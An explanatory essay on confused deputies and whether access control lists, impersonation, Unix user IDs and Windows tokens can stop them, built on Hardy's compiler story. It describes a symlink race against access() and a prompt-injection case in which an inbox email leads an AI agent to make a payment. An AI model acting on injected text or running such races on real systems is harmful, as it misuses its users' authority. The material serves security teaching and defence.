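# Can identity-based access checks prevent confused deputies?

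## What a confused deputy is and what an access check sees

A confused deputy is a program that ends up using its own permissions for someone who lacks them. The program carries out an outsider's request with powers the outsider could never have used directly, while doing more or less what it was built to do. The outsider doesn't have to break into the program or steal its password. Norm Hardy described the problem under that name in *The Confused Deputy* in 1988.

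Most computer systems decide whether to allow an operation by checking who is asking. People in computer security have long disagreed about whether these identity-based checks can stop a confused deputy. Researchers who favour capabilities, which are unforgeable references that both name a resource and permit its use, say that they cannot, even in principle. Defenders of identity-based checks propose repairs: the deputy can make its request under its caller's identity, the system can track everyone who influenced a request, a server can check which website a request came from, or an issuer can make credentials that work for only one purpose.

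This matters for any software that acts for people with real powers. Waterken's *The Confused Deputy rides again!* describes the web browser as such a program, because it attaches the user's login cookies to the requests it sends, whether the user or a visited page initiated them. The risk is greater with AI agents (models that call tools and services to carry out a task), because they read whatever arrives in an inbox and may treat a sentence in it as an instruction, a failure known as prompt injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". He thinks engineers can fix the classical confused deputy problem but can only reduce the risk and impact for language models.

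### Hardy's compiler

Hardy calls his story nearly true. It happened about eleven years before he published it, at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler, which translates source code into a form the machine can run, in a directory called SYSX. Users could give the compiler the name of a file to receive optional debugging output. Tymshare had also made it collect statistics on which language features people used and write them to a file called (SYSX)STAT. To allow this, the staff gave the compiler a "home files license", which let a program write files in its own directory.

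The same directory held (SYSX)BILL, the company's billing information. A user learned that name and gave it as the destination for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system to open the file for writing. The operating system found the compiler's license and opened the file, and the debugging text replaced the billing records.

Hardy considers several obvious repairs, and none of them works. The compiler could refuse to write any file outside the user's own directory, but people had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse to write anything in SYSX, but that name did not exist when programmers wrote the output code, and somebody with proper access to the directory might want output there. It could refuse BILL by name, but BILL was not the only sensitive file, and someone would have to update the compiler for each new one. The output code was correct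 when it was written, but in Hardy's account it became wrong on the day Tymshare granted the license, although the code itself had not changed. A reviewer looking for the bug would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file, and even then, Hardy says, it is not clear what the reviewer should do about them.

Hardy traces the problem to the compiler running with authority from two sources, the person who ran it and its license. The license was meant for writing statistics and the person's authority for writing debugging output, but the compiler had no way to specify which one to use. Tymshare added a system call for "switching hats" between the two, an early form of the repair in which a deputy acts under its caller's identity.

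Later authors usually tell a simpler story. In *Capability Myths Demolished* (2003), Miller, Yee and Shapiro give the compiler permission to write to BILL itself, because it records charges there, and the user names BILL as the debugging file. They note that this simplifies the original but makes the same point. Rajani, Garg and Rezk tell a similar story in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* (2016), except that compiled code, rather than debugging output, overwrites the bill.

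In Hardy's original example, the compiler needed access only to STAT but had a license for all of SYSX. A narrower license would have protected BILL but not STAT, which the user could have named just as easily, and Hardy notes that a solution must protect STAT too. In the simplified version, the compiler needs access to the file the user attacks, so narrowing its permissions doesn't help. From here on, "the compiler" means the simplified one, which has permission to write BILL, unless Hardy's original is named.

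### The vocabulary, applied to the compiler

A principal is anything to which a system can grant permissions. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) adds in its glossary that this makes a principal the unit of accountability. The user, Alice, and the compiler are both principals. An access control list (ACL) is kept with a resource and specifies which principals may do what to it. BILL's ACL lets the compiler write to it but doesn't let Alice.

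Authority is the ability to act on a resource, and designation is saying which resource one means. The compiler has authority over BILL and Alice has none, but anyone, including Alice, can designate BILL by typing its name. Miller and colleagues regard this gap between designation and authority as built into ACLs. An ACL is stored with the file and lists principals, so principals need a separate set of names to refer to files, and a name gives its holder no permission. In the attack, Alice supplied the designation and the compiler supplied the authority, and the operating system combined them without recording that they came from different parties.

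It could do so because the compiler's authority was ambient. Ambient authority applies to a request without the requester having selected it. A program that opens a file on a Unix-like system specifies the file's name and whether to read or write it, but not which of its permissions it is relying on. Miller and colleagues compare this to a world of doors without keys, where a door opens for anyone entitled to enter. People there cannot use the wrong key by mistake, but they also cannot choose to withhold one.

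A capability both designates an object and grants authority to access it. Saltzer and Schroeder define it as an unforgeable ticket that proves its presenter may access the object it names. In the capability version, the compiler holds a capability to BILL, which it uses only to record charges. Whoever runs the compiler gives it another capability, instead of a file name, for the debugging output. Alice holds no capability to BILL, so she cannot direct the debugging output there.

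### The check as a function

Lampson's model of access control shows exactly what an identity-based check has to work with. Lampson (1971), in *Protection*, describes a table with a row for each domain, meaning a context with its own set of powers (a principal, for present purposes), and a column for each object. Each cell holds attributes such as "read" or "write". When a domain tries to read a file, the program in charge of files looks in the cell for that domain and that file, and refuses if "read" is missing. An ACL is one column of the table, stored with its file. Put as a function, the check is:

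`allow = f(who asks, operation, resource)`

For the billing file, f(Alice, write, BILL) gives "no" and f(compiler, write, BILL) gives "yes", and both answers are what the owner of BILL wants. Now Alice runs the compiler and names BILL as her debugging file. During that run the compiler makes two requests:

- to record the charge: `f(compiler, write, BILL)`
- to write the debugging output: `f(compiler, write, BILL)`

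The owner wants the access check to allow the charge and deny the debugging output, but the arguments are identical, so the function returns the same answer to both. Tyler Close's *ACLs don't* (2009) starts from this loss of information and argues that ACL checks cannot give correct answers when more than two principals take part.

Better proof of identity would not help here. Lampson imagines a system that stamps every message with the sender's number, which the sender cannot alter. If process 6389 sends the numbers 31, 45 and 9, the receiver gets 6389, 31, 45, 9. In the compiler's case, the stamp would correctly identify the compiler as the requester, but the function has no argument for who chose the file name or which of its two jobs the compiler was doing.

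Real systems, including Hardy's, use more elaborate functions. The relevant part of his operating system's rule allowed a write if the person running the program could write the file, or if the program held the license and the file was in its home directory. Either source of authority was enough, regardless of which one the compiler was meant to use. The last time Hardy wrote out the full rule for opening a file, it contained fourteen "ands" and "ors". Each new clause that allowed something opened holes in programs that had been secure, and each new restriction broke programs that had been working.

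The same gap exists at the end of longer chains. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes a case in which a user asks an agent to summarize the invoices in an inbox, and one message contains text asking for a payment. The agent passes the request to a finance agent without passing on the read-only limit. The payment tool then receives a valid credential and executes the payment. It can authenticate its caller but cannot detect that a stranger's email prompted the payment.

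In Hardy's case, Alice ran the compiler herself, so a system that recorded the deputy's caller would have recorded the culprit. In the invoice case, the attacker only wrote an email, and the caller on record is the honest user. This difference matters for several of the proposed repairs.

One response is to give the access check more information. In *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, Siu, He and colleagues (2026) point out that the same command to delete a file can be routine cleanup or sabotage. They judge an agent's action against the user's prompt, the task history, the agent's memory, the state of its environment, the set of authenticated sources, and a map of which source may reach which. In principle, this is enough to distinguish the two deletions, but it requires knowing which input caused the agent to act. Siu and colleagues treat that as an idealised function that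 may have no perfect implementation. A compiler's write can be traced to a line of code, but nobody can yet reliably identify what caused a language model's action.

### Two definitions

People who agree on the compiler story still disagree about what else counts as a confused deputy. Alan Karp, a capability researcher, defined the term narrowly in March 2026 in the cap-talk mailing list thread *Gemini discusses Confused Deputy*: "A confused deputy uses its permissions on a resource designated by someone else." Miller, Yee and Shapiro defined it broadly in 2003. For them, a deputy is a program that must manage authorities from several sources, and a confused deputy is one that has been "manipulated into wielding its authority inappropriately".

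Karp offered his sentence as a teaching aid, and taken literally it covers too much. A web server uses its own permission to read whatever page a visitor designates, and this wrongs nobody. The definition needs the further condition that the person designating the resource has no permission to use it in that way. With that condition, it gives a clear test, which one can apply by asking who supplied the name. Karp uses it to exclude much of what other people call confused deputies. In his view, a script that runs with an administrator's powers and fails to clean up its input has a bug, but the bug is not what makes a confused deputy. Least privilege, the practice of giving a program only the permissions it needs, solves other problems. He also objects to having the deputy check its caller's permissions, since in some settings, such as those under American health privacy law, the deputy may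 not be allowed to know them.

The broad definition includes cases where the outsider doesn't designate any resource. Suppose Alice discovers that an odd comment in her source code makes the compiler record a charge of zero. The compiler chose BILL itself and used it for its proper purpose, but Alice's input made it write a false entry there. This makes the compiler a confused deputy under the broad definition, but only a faulty program under Karp's. Definitions written for AI agents tend to be broad. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026), for example, counts any case in which injected content turns an agent's legitimate authority toward the attacker's goal, regardless of who picked the resource.

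A definition of a confused deputy has to mention either who chose the object or what the access was for, because one of these is what separates an attack from an ordinary request. *Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) avoids the word "inappropriately" by defining the problem through cause and effect alone, with four conditions: the user lacks a certain right over an object, the deputy has that right, the user sends the deputy a request, and as a consequence the deputy exercises the right. But the compiler meets all four every time it bills an honest customer. Alice may not write to BILL, the compiler may, she asks it to compile something, and as a consequence it writes to BILL.

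The choice of definition affects how much each side can claim. Miller and colleagues use the broad definition, but their strongest statement about capabilities concerns the narrow case. They write that where designation and authority are inseparable, an attacker cannot succeed by naming a resource that is off limits to them. They are more careful about deputies in general, and grant that no security model can stop people from writing bad programs. Rajani and colleagues went further in 2016 with a formal definition under which capabilities fail to prevent some confused deputy attacks.

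Under the narrow definition, an identity-based check must determine who designated the resource and whether that party may use it. These are questions about identities, and at least some of the proposed repairs try to answer them. Under the broad definition, the check must also decide whether an outsider's influence on an otherwise proper request was acceptable, and a list of who may write to BILL has no information about that.

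## The argument that access control lists cannot solve it

After describing how Tymshare patched its operating system, Hardy gave his readers an exercise: "Show that access lists do not solve this problem." The compiler story contains everything needed for the proof, which takes only a few lines. Most of the disagreement is about how much the proof rules out.

### The proof

The compiler sends the same request, (compiler, write, BILL), in two situations:

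- Case A: it records Alice's charge, and the owner of BILL wants the answer to be yes.
- Case B: it writes debugging output to BILL because Alice named that file, and the owner wants the answer to be no.

Let f be any rule that decides from the requester, the operation and the resource alone. If f allows the compiler to write to the billing file, Alice can use the compiler to destroy the billing records. If f blocks the write, the compiler cannot bill anyone. So no f gives the right result for both Alice's request and ordinary billing.

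Making the rule more elaborate does not help. Heiser (2025) writes out a general ACL check as a short program in the university lecture *Object Capabilities*. The program goes down an ordered list of users and groups until an entry that covers the requester grants or forbids the access. Adding entries, groups or prohibitions could change the answer, but it would still be the same for both writes. An administrator could edit the list between the writes, but would have to know which one was coming next, and that is the missing information.

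Cutting down the compiler's permissions does not help either, as Hardy's warning about STAT implied. Even if the compiler keeps permission only for the file it needs for its own records, Alice can name that file, and the two cases arise again. The administrators can eliminate them only by removing that permission too, and then the compiler cannot do its job. They could instead hide the file's name, since Hardy's attacker first had to learn it. But a name that protects a file because outsiders cannot guess it serves partly as a permission. Rees (2009) notes that unguessable information and capabilities have similar properties.

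The proof holds only if both jobs use the same operation. In Heiser's version of the story, the compiler opens its log file for appending and the user's output file for ordinary writing. A system with a separate append permission could give the compiler only that permission on the log, so Alice's attempt to overwrite the log would fail. Basic Unix permissions (read, write and execute) do not distinguish appending from other writing. On systems that do, the protection lasts only until the compiler also needs to append to a file that a user names.

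### What the proof assumes

The proof assumes that the check has only the identity of the immediate requester. Many systems work this way. In *Testing for a confused deputy vulnerability* (2019), a mailing-list thread that Karp started, Miller gave the example of Ethereum, a blockchain whose programs, called contracts, can call one another. Each call includes an unforgeable field identifying its immediate sender. If contract A calls B and B then calls C, the field C receives identifies B but not A.

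Caller tracking and origin checks give the check more information about where a request came from, but this helps only if the information differs between case A and case B. The caller's name is the same in both, because Alice ran the compiler both times. If f gets a fourth input for the caller, it receives (Alice, compiler, write, BILL) in both cases and the proof still holds. Karp made a related point in the 2026 thread that Miller started: the code updating the log works for the compiler, not for the requester. To separate the cases, a system would have to track where the file name came from as well as who the caller was, because Alice's input supplied the name in only one of them.

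The proof also assumes that the compiler makes every request under one identity, but with impersonation it can use more than one. If the compiler records the charge as itself and writes the debugging output as Alice, the inputs become (compiler, write, BILL) and (Alice, write, BILL), and BILL's ordinary ACL allows the first and denies the second. Request-scoped tokens have a similar effect, because the deputy presents a different credential for each piece of work. Splitting the compiler into two programs with separate accounts, one for charges and one for users' output, would also protect BILL. But if the output program has permission to write every customer's files, Alice can name one of Bob's files and have it overwritten.

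Finally, the proof assumes that the compiler does not screen requests itself. The operating system cannot tell case A from case B, but the compiler can, because it has separate code for charges and debugging output. Before the debugging code opens a file, it could look up whether Alice may write there. This is a much stronger test than the repairs that Hardy rejected, in which the compiler inspected the file's name. It gives the right answer here, but every deputy must be able to find out what its callers may do, and must check this wherever it handles a name from outside.

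The proof covers only checks that decide from the deputy's own identity, with nothing else to separate the two cases. Impersonation and screening also use identity, through the same function f, but they work because they evaluate f with Alice as the requester at the right moment.

A capability check uses even less information than an ACL check. In Heiser's lecture it is a single line, which tests whether the capability the program presents includes the requested kind of access, regardless of who is asking. It gives the right result in both cases because the compiler presents its own capability for BILL in case A and whatever Alice handed over in case B. If a careless programmer sent the debugging output through the compiler's own BILL capability, the check would allow that too.

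Capabilities therefore also require the deputy to act differently in the two cases. Their advantage is that the easiest way to write the program is also the safe way. The debugging code writes to whatever Alice supplied, and she cannot supply BILL. With impersonation, the programmer has to remember to make the deputy change identity first, and if they forget, the attack works.

### More than two principals

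Close describes the same limit in *ACLs don't*. He argues that ACLs fail when an interaction involves more than two principals, because the system does not keep the information it needs for access decisions from one message to the next.

When Alice asks the file system for BILL directly, the sender of the request is also the person who chose the file. When she goes through the compiler, she sends it the name BILL, and the compiler sends that name to the file system in its own request. That second request comes from the compiler and doesn't show that Alice chose the file.

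Karp's 2019 test for the vulnerability has the same structure. Alice calls Bob's service and passes it the name of Carol's service. If Bob can't call Carol's service with Alice's permissions, Karp says, there is a confused deputy vulnerability. He expected people to answer that Bob should log in to Carol's service as Alice, and objected that this would give Bob far more power than the job requires. Another participant, Kevin Reid, pointed out an exception when Carol's service requires no permission from anyone, because there is then nothing to abuse. Miller concluded that the test is a great way to find confused deputies but does not define them.

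Close's claim needs a similar qualification. If the compiler ran with Alice's permissions and none of its own, the interaction would still involve Alice, the compiler and the owner of BILL, but the ACL would correctly refuse her. A third principal makes the error possible, and the error occurs when that principal has permissions that the person choosing the resource lacks.

Close thought that browsers made matters worse. He expected trouble whenever one site passes an identifier to another, as in his example of a printing site that gives a photo site the address of a file on a storage service that both use. In an exchange that van Kesteren (2009) quotes, Close added that inspecting the chain of callers is useless when widgets from several authors run in one page, because the browser assigns them all the same origin. Van Kesteren replied that a sandboxed frame would give an advertisement's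 code its own origin. That would help show which code is running, but not who chose the address that the code requests.

### Whether ACLs and capabilities are equivalent

Miller and colleagues reject as the "Equivalence Myth" the claim that ACLs and capabilities are formally equivalent, which would mean that one cannot succeed where the other fails. Lampson's table seems to support the claim, because its columns are ACLs and each row, which lists everything that one principal may do, looks like a list of capabilities. David Wagner agreed to go on record in their paper as having believed that the two were roughly equivalent until one of the group convinced him otherwise.

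They answer that the table shows permissions only at one moment. It has no rules for how its entries change, and it leaves out how a program refers to a file. With ACLs, a program needs file names that are separate from its permissions, whereas a capability can serve as the name itself.

Formal work supports both sides of this dispute, depending on what the model includes. Rajani and colleagues report that Chander, Dean and Mitchell proved access control equivalent to capabilities when capabilities are just rows in a table of permissions. In that model, a program can name a resource without having permission to use it. To study what happens when a program cannot do this, Rajani and colleagues built a small programming language with two alternative sets of rules. Under the access control rules, the system checks permission when code writes to a memory location. Under the capability rules,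 it checks earlier, when code obtains a writable reference to the location, and halts any code that obtains one it may not use.

They proved that the access control rules allow every step that the capability rules allow, and that the reverse is false. Their counterexample is a program that stores a reference to a forbidden location but never writes to it. The program finishes under access control, but the capability rules stop it before it finishes.

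The attack on the compiler uses this extra freedom. Alice puts a reference to a protected location where the compiler looks for its output file. The access control rules let her do this because she has not written to anything forbidden, and they later let the compiler write there because it has permission. The capability rules stop her at the first step. Rajani and colleagues also proved that under both sets of rules, code never changes a location that it lacks permission to write. Both therefore enforce the same policy about who may write what, but that policy doesn't cover who chose the location, so the equivalence does not settle whether a deputy can be confused.

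### Property A and Property D

Miller and colleagues compare security models on seven properties, labelled A to G, and use two of them to explain confused deputies.

Property D, "no ambient authority", holds when a program must select which permission it is using. The paper illustrates it with keys. Suppose the compiler holds a key to BILL for recording charges and accepts another key from Alice for the debugging output. As long as it uses each key for its own purpose, Alice cannot trick it. But a compiler that tries every key on its ring until the door opens is as easy to confuse as before. The compiler has to remember what each key is for, so it must know the context in which it received the key.

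Property A, "no designation without authority", holds when naming a resource always conveys permission to use it. Alice then cannot name BILL to the compiler, because she has no permission to pass along. Property A implies Property D because every request must name its resource, and if the name carries the permission, the requester selects the permission by naming the resource.

Their verdict is that avoiding confused deputies is "hopeless" without Property D and goes best with Property A. They rate several systems accordingly:

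| System | Does naming convey permission? (A) | Must the program select a permission? (D) | Rating for confused deputies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unix and Windows NT file permissions | no | no | danger |
| Capabilities as rows of Lampson's table | unspecified | no | danger |
| POSIX capabilities | no | no | danger |
| Capabilities as keys | no | yes | better |
| Unix file descriptors | yes | yes | best |
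| Object capabilities | yes | yes | best |

POSIX capabilities, despite the name, are flags that divide up the administrator's powers, such as the power to change the owner of any file. A program holding one does not select it for a particular request. Heiser likewise argues that the Linux version does nothing to prevent confused deputies. Moving permissions from the file's list to the program's list is therefore not enough, because the program also has to specify which permission it is using.

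"Hopeless" is too strong for a deputy that looks up its caller's permissions before acting, and elsewhere in the paper Miller and colleagues say only that the confusion is difficult to escape in ACL systems. Of the two properties, they claim only that Property A is impossible for an ACL. Rajani and colleagues agree, and see no reason in theory why an access control system could not have the other six. Tymshare's system call for switching hats let the compiler choose between two authorities, which was a limited form of Property D. Hardy reports that some applications soon needed more than two, and that the system had other kinds of authority besides access to files.

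Property D may not be enough on its own. Rajani and colleagues consider their access control model to have it, because code must present a reference before it can write. The compiler attack still succeeds in that model. One could object that the model doesn't really have Property D. The reference identifies the location, but the permission comes from the level of authority at which the code runs, so the compiler never chooses between Alice's permission and its own.

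Unix file descriptors are the hardest entry in the table to classify as either ACLs or capabilities. A descriptor is the handle that a program receives when it opens a file, and the program can pass it to another program. Suppose Alice's command shell opens her debugging file and passes the descriptor to the compiler. The operating system checks Alice's identity against the file's ACL when the shell opens it, and would refuse if she asked for BILL instead. The compiler then has no file name to misuse. The descriptor it receives is close to a capability, even though most people would describe Unix as using ACLs.

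### How the claim has fared

The IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy rejected Close's paper, *ACLs don't*, in 2009. He linked to the rejection on the paper's web page, next to the submission, and HP Laboratories published the paper as a technical report. Referees had earlier rejected the paper by Miller and colleagues.

In December 2009 the argument came up on a World Wide Web Consortium mailing list, where engineers were designing a way for web pages to send requests to other sites. Adam Barth doubted that a committee could resolve a difference in security philosophy that dated from the 1970s. Miller (2009) answered that if the ACL side had no defences left after forty years, it should concede. He knew of no paper that responded to the capability researchers' analysis of confused deputies. He said this could be because the scientific community was poorly equipped for the debate, because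 the flaws in the analysis were too obvious to need stating, or because nobody had found any.

Silence is weak evidence, but later work gives Miller's side better support. Rajani and colleagues, who dispute how much capabilities can prevent, say it is widely known that access control alone is insufficient. In their tests, the access control rules let through all five programs that contained an attack.

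Maciej Stachowiak of Apple raised a more practical objection on the same list. Even if the formal claim was true, he wrote, it did not show that ACL-based systems are always dangerously unsafe, or that the difference matters enough in a particular case to outweigh other considerations. The web already depended on cookies and origins, and he saw no clear plan for removing them. Rees replied that every approach carries risk, so the question should be which carries less. He also pointed out that the proposal covered only new kinds of request, so nobody had to remove anything that existing sites relied on. And he said the debate had mixed together two complaints, that a mechanism makes a policy impossible to implement and that it makes the policy difficult to implement. The two-case proof supports a claim of impossibility only while all its assumptions hold, and once a designer drops one, the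 argument is about difficulty.

In a 2015 exchange on a cryptography mailing list, Jerry Leichter argued that Miller and colleagues unfairly allowed capabilities to gain extensions while treating ACLs as fixed. He recalled that the VMS operating system combined a file's own list with others belonging to the process, the group and the whole system. Bill Frantz answered that the paper uses no extensions, because object capability systems date from the 1970s. His answer defends the paper's treatment of capabilities but doesn't settle whether ACLs should be allowed extensions. The proof implies that an extension helps only if it supplies something that differs between case A and case B. The lists in Leichter's example depend on which program is running and for whom, and those are the same in both cases.

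Capability researchers still think most people misunderstand the problem. In March 2026 Miller posted a chatbot's explanation of confused deputies to the cap-talk list, and Karp replied with corrections. He said many people he worked with on AI agent safety had the same misunderstandings. His objections to least privilege, to blaming faulty scripts and to having deputies check their callers' permissions come from this reply, as does his point about whom the log-writing code serves. The explanation blamed loose trust policies for the trouble in cloud services, but Karp says the trouble comes from having impersonation as the only way to delegate.

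Karp thinks nearly all the recommended remedies share the mistaken idea that the deputy has a bug. The proof supports him on least privilege, because a deputy with a single permission is still vulnerable to the attack. But his objection to having deputies check their callers' permissions concerns what deputies can find out in practice. If a deputy is allowed to look up its caller's permissions, the check gives the right answer to the compiler's problem.

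Jonathan Shapiro, one of Miller's co-authors in 2003, added that the deputy has no way to associate the permissions it intends to use with the resource. Karp objected that some certificate systems, such as zcaps and macaroons, do allow this, because their certificates list the delegated permissions and identify the resource. Miller replied that Shapiro had meant systems without capabilities, that zcaps are a capability system, and that macaroons are "cap-like enough". Karp accepted the correction. But if any credential that ties a permission to a resource counts as a capability, the claim that only capabilities let a deputy make this connection is close to true by definition. Some of the tokens that defenders of identity-based checks propose would then also count as capabilities.

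## Letting the deputy act under its caller's identity

The two-case proof works only if the compiler makes both requests under one identity. Tymshare changed its operating system so that this condition no longer held, and Unix and Windows have similar mechanisms. A deputy that uses them does its own work under its own identity and the work its caller asked for under the caller's identity.

### Switching hats

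A Tymshare system call let the compiler choose, before opening a file, whether to use its own license or the authority of the user running it. To write debugging output, it would open the file "by the authority vested in me by my invoker", in Hardy's words. If the user had named the billing file, the system would refuse to open it, because the user had no permission to write there.

This fixed the compiler. Hardy doesn't describe the applications that needed more than two authorities, but one example would be a program that Alice runs to combine her sales figures with Bob's and write the result to a report that only the program may change. The program needs Alice's authority to read her figures, Bob's to read his, and its own to write the report. Switching between its own authority and Alice's doesn't give it Bob's.

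The switch applied to opening files, and Hardy also found no obvious way to extend it to the system's other kinds of authority. The changes it required were scattered through the operating system.

Even with two authorities and nothing but files, switching between authorities only let the compiler choose which set of permissions to use. It could not select a single permission from a set. While it used Alice's permissions, it could write to every file Alice could write to, although she had named only one.

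### User IDs on Unix

A Unix process has a real user ID, which shows who started it, and an effective user ID, which the kernel (the core of the operating system) checks when the process opens a file. The two are normally the same. If a program's owner turns on its set-user-ID flag, the program starts with the owner's ID as its effective ID, no matter who runs it.

An administrator could use this for the compiler by creating an account called `fort`, allowing only that account to write to BILL, and making the compiler a set-user-ID program that `fort` owns. When Alice runs it, its real ID is `alice` and its effective ID is `fort`. The kernel also keeps a saved copy of `fort`, so the compiler can change its effective ID and change it back:

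1. It sets its effective ID to `alice`.
2. It opens the source and output files that Alice named.
3. It sets its effective ID back to `fort`.
4. It opens BILL and records the charge.

If Alice names BILL as her output file, the kernel checks `alice` at step 2 and refuses. The instructor in an MIT OpenCourseWare lecture on Hardy's paper considers this design "a little tricky" to get right but probably workable.

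The class also discussed splitting the program. A compiler with no special permissions would call a small set-user-ID program that only writes the log. Alice could no longer misdirect the compiler, but she could run the logging program herself and add false records, which is serious if the log determines people's bills. The instructor suggested letting only one group run the logger and giving the compiler that group's identity, though he disliked the effect on the user's own groups. The compiler would then again hold a permission that Alice lacks, though a much narrower one.

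A missing switch is easier to notice when the program belongs to an ordinary account than when it belongs to root, the administrator's account. If the programmer leaves out step 1, the compiler tries to read Alice's source code as `fort`. That fails if her files are private, so honest users complain immediately. A program owned by root can open almost any file, so every honest request works and the mistake stays hidden until someone exploits it.

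### Asking whether the caller may use the file

Alternatively, the deputy can check whether its caller has permission and then open the file under its own identity. The Unix call `access()` does this check, using the real user ID instead of the effective one. The set-user-ID compiler would call `access()` on the output file, then call `open()` if Alice may write to it.

The kernel answers this question correctly, but Alice can still overwrite BILL:

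1. She gives the compiler the name `out`, which belongs to an ordinary file of hers.
2. The compiler calls `access()` on `out`, and the kernel reports that Alice may write to it.
3. Alice deletes `out` and replaces it with a symbolic link, a file that redirects to another one, pointing to BILL.
4. The compiler calls `open()` on `out`. The kernel follows the link to BILL, checks the effective ID, `fort`, and opens the file.

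The gap between steps 2 and 4 may be very short, but Alice can run the compiler as often as she likes and has to succeed only once. Linux man-pages' *Manual of ACCESS(2) (v6.01)* warns of this gap and advises against using `access()` for this purpose. It recommends switching the effective ID to the real one and then calling `open()`. Mason (1994) had made the same suggestion on the security mailing list Bugtraq, in reply to someone who quoted a FreeBSD manual page telling programmers never to use `access()`. He found it easier to swap the two IDs, open the file and swap them back.

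Switching to the caller's identity works because `open()` finds the file and checks permission in a single operation. If Alice puts the link in place before the call, the kernel checks her identity against BILL's permissions and refuses. If she does it afterwards, the compiler already has the original file open, so the link has no effect.

Because of this race, looking up the caller's permissions solves the compiler's problem only if the name still refers to the same file when the deputy uses it. The MIT OpenCourseWare lecture adds two practical objections to repeating the kernel's checks inside the deputy. A programmer can leave out a check, and the copied rules become outdated when the kernel's rules change.

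### Impersonation on Windows

Windows describes a user's identity, groups and privileges in a record called an access token. Each process has a primary token, and a single thread (one line of execution within the process) can temporarily take on another. A typical server receives requests through a named pipe, a channel between two programs, and has access to files that its clients may not be allowed to use. Microsoft's *Impersonating a Named Pipe Client* describes the sequence:

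1. A client connects to the pipe and sends a request.
2. A server thread reads the request and calls `ImpersonateNamedPipeClient`, which gives the thread the client's token.
3. The thread tries to open the file. Windows checks the client's token against the file's ACL and allows or refuses the access.
4. The thread calls `RevertToSelf`, which removes the client's token, and continues as the server.

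If the client is Alice and the file is BILL, the check at step 3 is f(Alice, write, BILL), and the ACL gives the right answer.

The system also limits how far a server may go in acting as its client. Microsoft's *Impersonation Levels (Authorization)* lists four levels:

| Level | What the server can do |
|---|---|
| Anonymous | Neither identify nor impersonate the client |
| Identification | Read the client's identity and privileges, but not act as the client |
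| Impersonation | Act as the client on the server's own machine |
| Delegation | Act as the client on other machines too |

A client on the same machine as the server can choose the impersonation level when it connects. The default for named pipes is impersonation, so a client that doesn't choose a level lets the server act as the client locally. For a connection from another machine, Windows ignores the client's choice and uses a setting on the server's account. If an administrator has enabled that account for delegation, the server gets the delegation level even if the client asked for identification only.

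The identification level lets a deputy check its caller's permissions itself. Microsoft's *SECURITY_IMPERSONATION_LEVEL enumeration (winnt.h)* recommends it for servers that manage their own objects, such as a database with tables and views. The `access()` race is less of a threat there because Alice cannot replace a table inside the database unless the database lets her, whereas she can replace a file in her own directory while the compiler is working.

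If the impersonation call at step 2 fails, the thread keeps the server's identity, and everything it does for the client afterwards runs with the server's permissions. Microsoft's *ImpersonateNamedPipeClient function (namedpipeapi.h)* therefore tells programmers to check the result every time and to carry out no client requests after a failure. A server that ignores the result can pass its tests and still become a confused deputy when the call fails.

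Impersonation also does not carry over to programs that the server starts. Windows gives them the server's primary token, even if the thread that launches them is impersonating a client. Suppose a server impersonates Alice and launches a file converter on a file name she supplied. The converter runs as the server and can open BILL, even though the programmer had switched to Alice's identity.

Hardy's problem with more than two authorities also arises here. Microsoft's *Why doesn't RevertToSelf undo the most recent SetThreadToken?* (2016) describes a customer whose service impersonated a client and then needed a second, unrelated identity to fetch some information. The service then called `RevertToSelf`, which the customer expected to restore the client's identity. Instead, the call removed all impersonation and returned the thread to the service's own account, Network Service. If the service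 had then opened a file named by the client, Windows would have checked Network Service's access instead of the client's.

### Copying a file with two identities

A deputy such as a backup service must choose which identity to use for each access. Suppose customers call `copy(source, destination)` to make backups. Alice wants to back up a file from her home directory, which she can read, to a vault that only the service can write to. The service should therefore read the source with Alice's permissions and write to the destination with its own.

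| Identity used for the two opens | Alice backs up her own file | Alice names Bob's salary file as the source |
|---|---|---|
| The service for both | Succeeds | Succeeds, and Alice can retrieve Bob's file |
| Alice for both | Fails at the destination | Fails at the source |
| Alice for the source, the service for the destination | Succeeds | Fails at the source |

The first row assumes that the service can read every customer's files, which it must if it does all its work under its own identity. Karp (2022) notes that many services run this way today. Only the third row is right in both columns. The code for it is short:

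```
become Alice
in = open(source, read)
become the service
out = open(destination, write)
copy the contents of in to out
```

The service needs Alice's identity only for the first `open`. That call returns a handle to one particular file, and the service can keep reading from the handle after it switches back to its own identity. With impersonation, the service turns each name into a handle under the right identity, and that handle is very close to a capability.

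If the programmer forgets to switch to Alice, the result is the first row, and if they forget to switch back, it is the second. The second mistake breaks every backup, so the programmer will find it within minutes. The first is harder to notice because legitimate backups still succeed. Only a test in which a customer asks for a file they aren't allowed to read would reveal it.

The third row also assumes that the service picks the destination. If Alice can name it, she can name the place in the vault that holds Bob's backup, and the service will use its own permissions to overwrite it. Switching to Alice's identity for the write doesn't help, because she isn't allowed to write to the vault directly, even to her own backups, so every write would fail. The service has to write under its own identity, which can write anywhere in the vault, so it needs to keep a record of who owns each backup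 and check it before each write.

The code also depends on opening the two files separately. Karp compares this with a service that sends the whole job to a storage system in one request, with the user's credentials and its own attached. Programmers often combine requests this way for speed or reliability, or because an older system requires it. The component that decides access then has two credentials and two files but cannot tell which credential goes with which file, so it may accept the service's credential for a destination that the user chose. Karp says that if the request matched each credential to a file, the system would be very close to a capability system.

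David Chadwick, who works on verifiable credentials (signed digital statements about a person), maintained that a gatekeeper that checks only the user's credentials, and never presents its own, cannot be confused unless it has a bug. Karp (2022) replied that this avoids the problem only in the simplest case, with one argument. Chadwick's arrangement is safe when the user may use every resource in the request, as when Alice copies one of her own files to another. In the backup example, it gives the result in the second row of the table, where the system is secure but never makes a backup.

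### Giving the deputy everything the caller has

Karp's other objection to Chadwick was that a deputy with the user's credentials can use any of the user's permissions. The backup service needs to read only one of Alice's files, but while it impersonates her, it can read or delete all of them and write to any shared folder that she can. If an attacker takes over the service, every customer who calls it is exposed. On Unix, a program that Alice starts herself normally has her file permissions anyway, but a separate service gets them only through impersonation.

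Microsoft's *Impersonation* notes that impersonating a client can either restrict or expand a server's access, depending on the client's permissions. A deputy with few permissions of its own gains much more access while it impersonates an administrator.

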